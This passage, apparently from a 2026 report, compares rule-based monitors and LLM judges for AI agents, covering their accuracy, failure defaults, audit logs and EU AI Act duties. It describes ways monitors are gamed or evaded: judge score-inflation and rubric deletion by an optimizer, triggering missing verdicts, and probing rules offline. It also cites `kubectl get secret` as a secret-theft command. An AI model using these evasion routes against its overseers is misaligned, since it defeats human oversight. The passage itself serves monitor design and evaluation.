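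Language models drafted each check along with three correct answers and three nearly correct ones. Another model then looked for answers that the check would wrongly accept or reject. Finally, software confirmed that the check accepted the correct answers and rejected the nearly correct ones and the answers to other tasks. This process exposed five errors in the benchmark's answer key.

The finished checks agreed with a GPT-5.1 judge on 99.87% of an expert agent's runs, or all but one in roughly 760. But the judge rated 98.57% of the runs successful, so a check that accepted everything would have agreed almost as often. The result is good evidence that the checks rarely reject correct answers, but weak evidence that they catch wrong ones, because the sample contained at most about a dozen failures. The checks also test whether an agent found the right answer, which is easier to specify than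 whether it behaved safely.

*Local-First RSI* (Wang and Kong, 2026) tested what happens when text is optimized to score well with its grader. In the experiment, dated 30 November 2026, one small language model repeatedly edited a prompt that told another how to condense text, and a grader decided whether to keep each edit. The deterministic grader counted how many required items survived in the condensed text and kept an edit only if the improvement was statistically significant. The alternative grader, a 32-billion-parameter judge model running on the same laptop, scored the condensed text from 0 to 10.

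The researchers planted edits designed to impress a grader without improving the result, such as adding flattery or echoing the grading criteria. Over three trials, the judge kept 8 of 11 planted edits and the deterministic grader kept none. The deterministic grader kept the one real improvement in every trial, while the judge never kept it. In the first trial, the judge raised its score by 3 points for flattery and lowered it slightly for the real improvement.

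Flattery can't affect code that only counts required items, so this part of the result is convincing. The rest is less convincing, partly because the deterministic grader's own scoring method defined what counted as a real improvement, and that improvement came from an edit that the same kind of grader had accepted earlier. No planted edit targeted the code, for example by listing every required item without making sense. The judge was also small, and the three trials used the same real improvement and mostly the same planted edits.

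### Where fixed rules miss the meaning

The strongest evidence against fixed rules comes from Yang's *AgentTrust*. Each monitor could allow an agent's action, allow it with a warning, send it for review or block it. Yang's 170 rules did well on 630 actions from an existing benchmark, but earlier work had already patched them to fix errors on that benchmark. The rules did badly on 189 new actions, many of them attacks that resembled ordinary work.

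| Monitor | Actions | Exactly right | False positive rate | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 170 rules | 630 familiar | 95.4% | 2.1% | 6.1% |
| 170 rules | 189 new | 48.1% | 22.4% | 52.9% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 189 new | 85.2% | 1.7% | 4.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 189 new | 84.1% | 0% | 2.3% |
| GPT-5.5 | 189 new | 83.6% | 6.9% | 1.1% |

The percentages imply that the rules missed 46 of 87 dangerous actions and flagged 13 of 58 harmless ones. The samples are small, but the gap is too large to be due to chance. A weaker judge, from DeepSeek, was right more often than the rules but flagged 31% of harmless actions.

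Yang then wrote more rules for cloud services. Accuracy on actions involving cloud credentials rose from 40% to 70%, but it didn't change for databases (29%), monitoring tools (59%) or software packages (50%). Opus 4.8 scored 86%, 78% and 80% on the last three. Yang attributes the difference to pairs of actions that look alike. For example, an engineer's agent might run `kubectl get secret` to find out why a program is failing, and a hijacked agent might run the same command to steal the password.

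The test is strong evidence against pattern matching but weaker evidence against rules that compare an action with its context, so it doesn't prove Yang's claim that rules can't detect such threats. A judge that saw only the command couldn't tell those two actions apart either. It needs other information, such as the user's request, which some fixed rules can also use. Yang's added rules mostly looked for patterns in a single action. A data-flow check could detect the contents of a password file in an outgoing message, and a Sapien policy might not permit reading secrets for that request.

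Hu, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *SABER*, used rules with more context, but these still missed many harmful runs. They gave 13 models 716 coding tasks in sandboxed projects. Each task came with patterns for dangerous commands an agent might run, and other code checked for effects such as destroyed files or leaked data. These checks caught 4,198 of 6,015 harmful runs (69.8%). An LLM judge found the rest, including some where each step looked reasonable but the steps together did harm. Human auditors agreed with 350 of the 360 labels they sampled. A live monitor's rules would probably catch a smaller share, since the researchers knew which dangers they had built into each task.

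*MAS-Guard* reaches a similar conclusion for groups of agents, where many attacks use permitted routes, valid formats and allowed tools. Adding a language model's check on what each agent was authorized to do cut the attack success rate on one benchmark from 23.8% to 12.0%. The paper warns that such checks can also block harmless messages.

Rules that allow actions can also fail. *HASTE* (2026) describes a monitor that blocks prohibited actions, allows read-only and routine ones, and sends only the rest to an LLM. This saves model calls, but `kubectl get secret` is a read-only command whether the agent is debugging or stealing. If the monitor allowed it as read-only, a theft would never reach the LLM.

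### Errors that repeat

| | Fixed rule | Frozen classifier | LLM judge |
|---|---|---|---|
| Repeatability | Exact | Exact on the same software and hardware | Varies, unless the server runs in a deterministic mode that works for the model |
| Coverage | What its author anticipated | Cases like its training data | Anything it can infer from the text, including intent |
| False alarms | Rare on familiar cases, common on lookalikes | Depend on the threshold and the domain | Under 7% for strong judges on Yang's new actions, much higher in some other tests |
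| Cost | Almost nothing | About a millisecond of computing | From about 0.02 to 1.5 cents, and 1 to 33 seconds |
| Upkeep | New rules for new threats | New labelled examples for new domains | New tests whenever the model or prompt changes |
| Audit | The flag can name the rule and the matching text | The score combines many small weights | The explanation may not reflect the real cause |

A deterministic detector can give the same wrong verdict every time. Wang and Kong's deterministic grader rejected every edit for 30 rounds, even though the average scores had risen. Early versions scored too coarsely and mixed differences between tasks with differences between prompts, so real improvements looked like noise. Rerunning the comparison on the same scores would have repeated the error, and majority voting can't correct a deterministic rule because every vote is the same.

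Repeatable errors are also useful to attackers. Anyone with a copy of the rules can test commands privately until one passes, and that command will work against every company that uses the same rules. Attackers could test commands against an LLM judge too, but a command that passed once might fail the next time.

Determinism also makes errors easier for the operator to find and fix. The operator needs only one replay, instead of dozens, to see what a rule does with a given input. After changing a rule, the operator can rerun it on every saved trajectory at almost no cost and list which verdicts changed, but still needs correct labels for those cases to know whether the new verdicts are better.

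## Which decisions can rest on an LLM verdict, and what record makes it auditable?

An LLM's verdict is enough reason to alert a person, and it can support a safety score if people have checked a sample of the verdicts. It shouldn't be the only safeguard before an irreversible action. Between these cases, people who build monitors disagree about what a model may block or approve on its own.

### Only fixed checks should block a merge

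bamdad argues against letting an LLM judge decide whether developers may merge a code change. "A control that flips its verdict on a retry is not a control," the blogger writes. Suppose a judge flags an unsafe change in 90% of runs. A developer who takes the flag for a false alarm and reruns the check up to twice has a 27% chance of getting a pass (1 − 0.9³), without meaning any harm. A fixed check, such as the taint-flow check, returns the same result on every retry, needs no threshold and keeps working when the judge's vendor has an outage.

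An operator could prevent such retries by storing the first verdict for each version of the code, but a trivial edit would create a new version and another chance to pass.

The main weakness of fixed checks is coverage, since they can miss things such as text that the agent has rewritten. A team that blocks merges only on fixed checks needs another way to find what they miss, and bamdad still recommends LLM judges for investigating failures.

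### A mechanical rejection overrides the LLM's approval

The main argument for a middle position comes from *LLM-as-a-Judge Is Not an Oracle*, a September 2026 field report by the engineer Vansh Wahi. Wahi ran systems in which one model repeatedly rewrote another model's prompt, and software kept the changes that scored well. An LLM judge produced many of the scores. The work covered contract review, legal compliance and code quality.

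In an early prototype, a judge rated code from 1 to 5, and an optimizing model rewrote the judge's prompt to bring its ratings closer to a set of reference ratings. It went wrong as follows:

1. The optimizer replaced the judge's entire scoring rubric with a placeholder.
2. The judge, which now had no criteria, wrote prose without the required rating fields.
3. The parser silently recorded a 3 for every quality.
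4. Those 3s happened to be closer to the reference ratings than the original judge's scattered 4s and 5s, so the average error fell from 0.96 to 0.92.
5. The selection software promoted the broken prompt, and only a human audit caught it.

The parser and the selection software were both deterministic code that worked as designed, so the incident is as much a warning about careless checks in such code as about LLM judges.

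Wahi lists eleven kinds of failure. Some came from the judge, which gave 4 out of 5 to a library that contained production passwords and silently discarded errors. Others came from the data, as when a faulty pipeline labelled a contract compliant although it lacked required tax clauses. The optimizer then deleted correct tax rules from the agent's prompt to match the label. In another case, the optimizer found keywords that raised the judge's scores. The pass rate for the agent's reasoning rose from 23.1% to 80.0%, but the agent was no better at finding defects.

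Wahi's remedy is an acceptance rule. For a current prompt S and a proposed patch p:

apply p only if M(p) = 1 and T(p) = 1

keep p only if R(S with p) ≥ R(S)

M is 1 if the patch passes four mechanical checks: it adds at most one example, makes at most two edits (five for a restructuring), contains no instruction to read files or run commands, and leaves the prompt's output format intact. T is 1 if an LLM grader, which Wahi calls the Teacher, approves the patch. R is the share of training cases that pass.

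Wahi describes the Teacher as an advisor, but under this rule its rejection also stops a patch. It can't approve a patch that failed a mechanical check. bamdad's objection would still apply if a company used the same rule for merges, because the LLM might not reject the same change on a retry.

Over about 50 iterations, the system logged 13 rejections or reversals. In six of them, the Teacher had approved a patch that then lowered the pass rate, in one case from 88.9% to 33.3%. These six are the best evidence against letting an LLM grader make the final decision. Some of the others are weaker evidence. Two were patches that broke a limit on examples stricter than the one in the optimizer's instructions, and a third was the placeholder incident, in which the software had promoted the bad prompt.

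The evidence also comes from small tests. Most of the ten test suites have fewer than 20 cases, each pass rate comes from a single run, and all the models belong to one family. People rated only 15 of the 54 code directories, and a model rated the rest. Wahi stresses that the Teacher is an LLM judge with the same weaknesses as the others. On two of the contract suites, an LLM also decides whether each case passes, so R depends on an LLM too, and a model's verdicts still determine which patches survive.

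### Questions of intent need a language model

Whether a command is acceptable can depend on what the user asked for. A rule can detect a force-push, but it can't determine whether "tidy up this branch" permits one. Anthropic tested a version of auto mode's classifier that read the agent's tool calls but not the user's messages. It had the lowest miss rate of the versions tested, but it blocked actions that users had plainly asked for.

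OpenAI made a similar choice for the reviewing agent in Codex. Trębacz and colleagues write that it "sacrifices determinism for expressivity". The agent approves some risky actions if the user explicitly requested them. It approved 99.1% of real requests to leave the sandbox and refused 90.3% of synthetic actions in which an agent did more than the user wanted. Testers still found ways to mislead it, and Trębacz and colleagues don't expect this kind of system to provide deterministic guarantees.

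A model can only identify intent that the user has expressed. In the tests with vague requests, none of the three products reliably separated permitted from forbidden actions until the researchers stated the missing rules.

A fixed rule can often enforce a user's stated limit more dependably than an LLM judge. Claude Code's classifier treats an instruction such as "don't push" as a reason to block, but it finds that instruction by rereading the conversation at every check. If the software shortens a long conversation and drops the message, the limit is lost. In its documentation, Anthropic recommends a deny rule for anyone who needs "a hard guarantee", because deny rules apply before the classifier and in every mode. A deny rule blocks only the commands it matches, however, and Anthropic warns that one feature, Code Mode, lets the agent run shell commands in forms the rules don't match.

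Claude Code's rules can also approve actions, whereas Wahi's mechanical checks can only reject them. An action that matches a user's allow rule normally runs without reaching the classifier, which is risky if the rule is broad. Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizable minority of Codex users inside OpenAI had allowed every command beginning with `python`, which can run almost anything. Claude Code suspends rules like this while auto mode is on.

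### Testing the positions on four decisions

Which position works best depends on what each error costs. Let F be the cost of blocking something harmless, U the cost of letting something unsafe through, and p the probability that it is unsafe. Blocking has an expected cost of (1 − p)F and allowing has an expected cost of pU, so blocking is cheaper when:

p > F / (F + U)

If a false alarm costs $1 in delay and losing a production database costs $10,000, the operator should block a deletion whenever the probability of harm exceeds 0.01%. LLM judges' probabilities are rarely that accurate. To confirm that actions with a score of 0.01% are that safe, the operator would need about 30,000 labelled examples with no unsafe action among them. Requiring explicit approval for such deletions makes more sense than relying on a score.

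| Decision | Can people undo a mistake? | What an LLM verdict can reasonably do | If the judge is unavailable |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocking a merge | Usually, by reverting the change | Advise the person who approves the merge | Fixed checks and the human reviewer decide |
| Stopping an agent's action | Often not | Block, or approve what no fixed rule forbids | Deny the action, then retry or ask the user |
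| Alerting a person | Yes, apart from the time spent | Raise the alert on its own | Save the record and judge it later |
| Reporting a safety score | Yes, but others may already have relied on it | Supply the verdicts, with human labels as a check | Report how many verdicts are missing |

**Merges** suit the first position best. The code stays the same while people examine it, and a delay of an hour rarely matters. Releases that expose a password or reach customers' devices are harder to reverse, so fixed checks for those cases are more valuable. An LLM can still be one safeguard among several, as at OpenAI, where a model automatically reviews every proposed code change. By default, Claude Code's classifier blocks the agent from merging a change that no human has approved.

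**An agent's actions** need a combination of the second and third positions. The agent can't wait for a person at every step, and many decisions depend on what the user wanted. Fixed rules should forbid the few actions that would be disastrous in any context, and the LLM can decide the rest. In Claude Code, a refusal does little harm because the agent usually finds another way to do the task, so the classifier can be cautious.

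An alert can rest on an LLM verdict alone. If a review costs $5 and a successful intervention saves $500, alerting is worthwhile whenever the chance of a successful intervention is above about 1%, and a wrong alert wastes only a few minutes. But an alert helps only if the person pays attention, and Anthropic reports that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. An operator who replaces a block with a request for approval may remove most of the protection.

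**Safety scores** often depend on an LLM because fixed checks can't assess the material. Random flips in the verdicts mostly cancel out, but a bias they share doesn't. Wahi's keyword example shows how much developers can inflate a score by optimizing against the judge. They should keep the final test cases out of that optimization and compare a sample of verdicts with human labels.

Fixed checks can also expose a false score. One of Wahi's contract cases mistakenly required the agent to flag an ordinary full stop as a fatal violation. Agents that scored 47 out of 47 passed this case because they found the answers in stored files. Without access to those files, the pass rate was 68.1%. Wahi now deliberately adds impossible cases so that a perfect score triggers an investigation.

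### When the judge returns no verdict

Products handle judge failures differently. Claude Code denies an action if its server returns no verdict, and it can stop the agent's turn after ten such responses in a row. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, Codex reports timeouts separately from refusals and tells the agent that a timeout alone doesn't prove the action unsafe.

By contrast, OpenAI's *Quickstart* for its Guardrails software library describes a default that lets a request continue when a check fails to run. The software records the check as not triggered, and a developer has to turn on a strict mode to get an error instead. The library's name for this default is "fail-safe", so an operator who relies on the name could easily expect the opposite.

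Denying every action that has no verdict blocks safe actions too. If the judge returned no verdict on 1% of 10,000 actions, the software would block 100 of them, compared with about 40 false alarms at auto mode's published rate. Allowing those 100 actions appears to add little risk if failures are random. If 10 of the 10,000 actions were unsafe, the judge would fail to return a verdict on an average of only 0.1 of them, whereas the classifier would miss 1.7 anyway.

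But missing verdicts may not be random, and an attacker might be able to cause them. Anthropic's list of error messages includes one for a transcript that exceeds the classifier's length limit and another for a safeguard that refuses the classifier's request. If actions go through when a verdict is missing, an attacker could try to make the transcript too long or fill it with text that triggers the safeguard. DeepSeek-V4-Pro's missing verdicts were concentrated in unsafe runs, so the problem can arise even without an attacker. Denying the action is therefore the better default when it could do lasting damage, while an alerting system can queue the record.

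Missing verdicts limit what anyone can conclude from a safety score. If a judge flags 30 of 1,000 cases and returns no verdict on 20, its flag rate would have been between 3% and 5% had it returned all the verdicts. Counting the 20 as safe would give a rate of 3% and hide the uncertainty.

### What to store with each verdict

A Judge Card describes how a judge performs across many cases, but an auditor investigating an incident needs the record of one verdict. Suppose the log in the web-page case contains only the word "safe". The auditor can't tell whether the judge saw the web page, scored the command 0.70 against a threshold of 0.8, or never answered. The following record would distinguish these possibilities.

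| Item to store | What an auditor can check with it |
|---|---|
| Payload | Whether the judge received the relevant evidence and the right policy |
| Model version | Which model gave the verdict, including any fallback model |
| Settings | Temperature, seed, reasoning effort and length limit |
| Raw answer, with token probabilities if available | What the model returned before any software interpreted it |
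| Parser version | Whether the same code turns the answer into the recorded verdict |
| Repeats | Every run and the rule for combining them, so nobody can keep only the convenient verdict |
| Threshold | Whether the score should have led to a flag |

The audit record should take the model version from the call itself, because defaults change. The classifier in Claude Code's auto mode originally ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 and now normally runs on Sonnet 5. Users can choose another model, but Claude Code sometimes ignores that choice and writes the reason to its debug log.

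The record needs a separate field for errors. Mend's *Error handling*, the documentation for another guardrail library, describes a result that marks a check as "execution_failed" when the check itself doesn't work, and keeps this separate from a policy violation. The request can still continue, but an auditor can find every case where the check didn't work.

The log should also record the action that ran and anyone who overrode the verdict. Other software can alter a command after the judge has approved it, and Claude Code can deny an action for that reason. In Codex, a user can approve one retry of a refused action. The reviewing agent then checks the action again with that approval in its input, and can still refuse. If the second verdict differs from the first, an auditor with no record of the approval might mistake the change for random variation.

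Full payloads can contain passwords and personal data, so the audit log needs protection. Deleting them makes the log safer to keep but may make an exact replay impossible. An operator could encrypt the full payload and give most reviewers a redacted copy.

### What an auditor can check after the model is gone

Once a vendor retires a hosted model, an auditor can still check much of a good record. They can rerun the saved parser, apply the threshold, compare the payload with the full trajectory, and rerun any deterministic detector. They can also count disagreements among stored repeats and ask people whether the verdict was right. They can't get new verdicts from that model, so they can't measure its flip rate on a case it judged only once. They can run a newer model on the case, but its verdict won't show what the retired model would have decided.

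Once the model is gone, it is also much harder to establish why the judge reached its verdict. A written rationale is weak evidence, especially if it comes after the score. The model generates text in order, so an explanation written after the score can't have produced it. In Wahi's code-quality test, asking for the rationale first raised exact agreement with the reference ratings from 42.6% to 51.9%, or five more of the 54 directories. This suggests that an explanation written first can affect the score, but it may still omit what mattered most.

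An auditor can test a rationale by changing the evidence it cites. If the rationale for flagging the shell command is that the text came from an untrusted page, the auditor can replace the page's text and replay the payload several times. If the flag rate stays the same, the page's text was probably not necessary for the verdict. It may still have contributed, because other evidence could be enough on its own. These tests require the original model, so operators should run them on important cases before the vendor retires it.

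An open model gives an auditor more options, because the operator can save its weights and serving software. Even then, an exact replay may require the same hardware.

Some monitors provide little explanation. In most sessions, Claude Code gives only the name of the rule that the classifier matched, such as "Data Exfiltration". An auditor can compare that rule with the action, but can't see how the classifier decided that the rule applied.

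### What the EU AI Act requires

The EU has passed rules on logs and consistent performance, but they don't apply yet. They cover only AI systems that the EU AI Act classes as high-risk. Examples include systems that analyze CVs, evaluate school exams or assess loan applications (Euronews, 2025).

An amendment that took effect in July 2026 postponed these duties. According to Orrick's *EU AI Act Update* (2026), they now apply from these dates:

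- **2 December 2027** for high-risk uses listed in Annex III of the Act, which include the examples above.
- **2 August 2028** for high-risk systems covered by the EU product legislation listed in Annex I.

A system in the first group that is on the market before its date has to comply only if its provider substantially modifies it afterwards. Systems intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 even if they are not modified.

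A safety monitor isn't automatically high-risk. If it is part of a high-risk system, such as an agent that screens job applicants, the duties for that system would probably apply to it too. A monitor could also count as a "safety component" of a regulated product. The amendment narrowed this term to systems intended to prevent or mitigate risks to health and safety, although a system whose failure would endanger people still qualifies. A monitor that stops an AI-controlled medical device from giving a dangerous dose might therefore qualify, but one that stops a coding agent from deleting a branch probably would not.

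The EU AI Act's *Article 12* requires high-risk systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The logs must help identify risks and substantial modifications, and support monitoring once the system is in use. The article doesn't mention payloads, temperatures or parser versions. It lists minimum log contents, such as the start and end of each use, only for remote biometric identification systems. Bauer Group's *Record-Keeping*, a company's draft compliance guide, presents these contents as a minimum for high-risk systems in general, which the article's text doesn't support.

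According to the same guide, organizations using a high-risk system must keep its logs for at least six months. That minimum may be too short if someone later disputes a monitor's verdict. *EU AI Act Article 12 and the Interaction-Trace Gap* (2026) argues that even logs of inputs, outputs, tool calls, model versions and errors don't fulfill Article 12's purpose, because many serious failures arise from how people delegate to a system and oversee it. This is the paper's interpretation of Article 12, which can be read in other ways.

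Article 15 requires high-risk systems to achieve an appropriate level of accuracy and robustness, and to "perform consistently in those respects throughout their lifecycle". The full text, on the European Commission's *Article 15* page, sets no maximum error rate or flip rate. A consistent level of performance doesn't seem to require the same verdict every time for the same input, so an LLM judge could comply in principle. But a provider who never measured its accuracy after a model update would struggle to show that the judge complied.

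The provider must also state in its instructions the system's accuracy levels and the metrics used. A single accuracy figure for a monitor could satisfy the wording, but customers would learn little from it about misses or false alarms. Article 15 also requires systems to be as resilient as possible to errors and faults, and mentions backup or fail-safe plans as one way to do this. It doesn't specify whether a system should block or allow an action when its judge fails, so the provider has to make that choice and be able to defend it.
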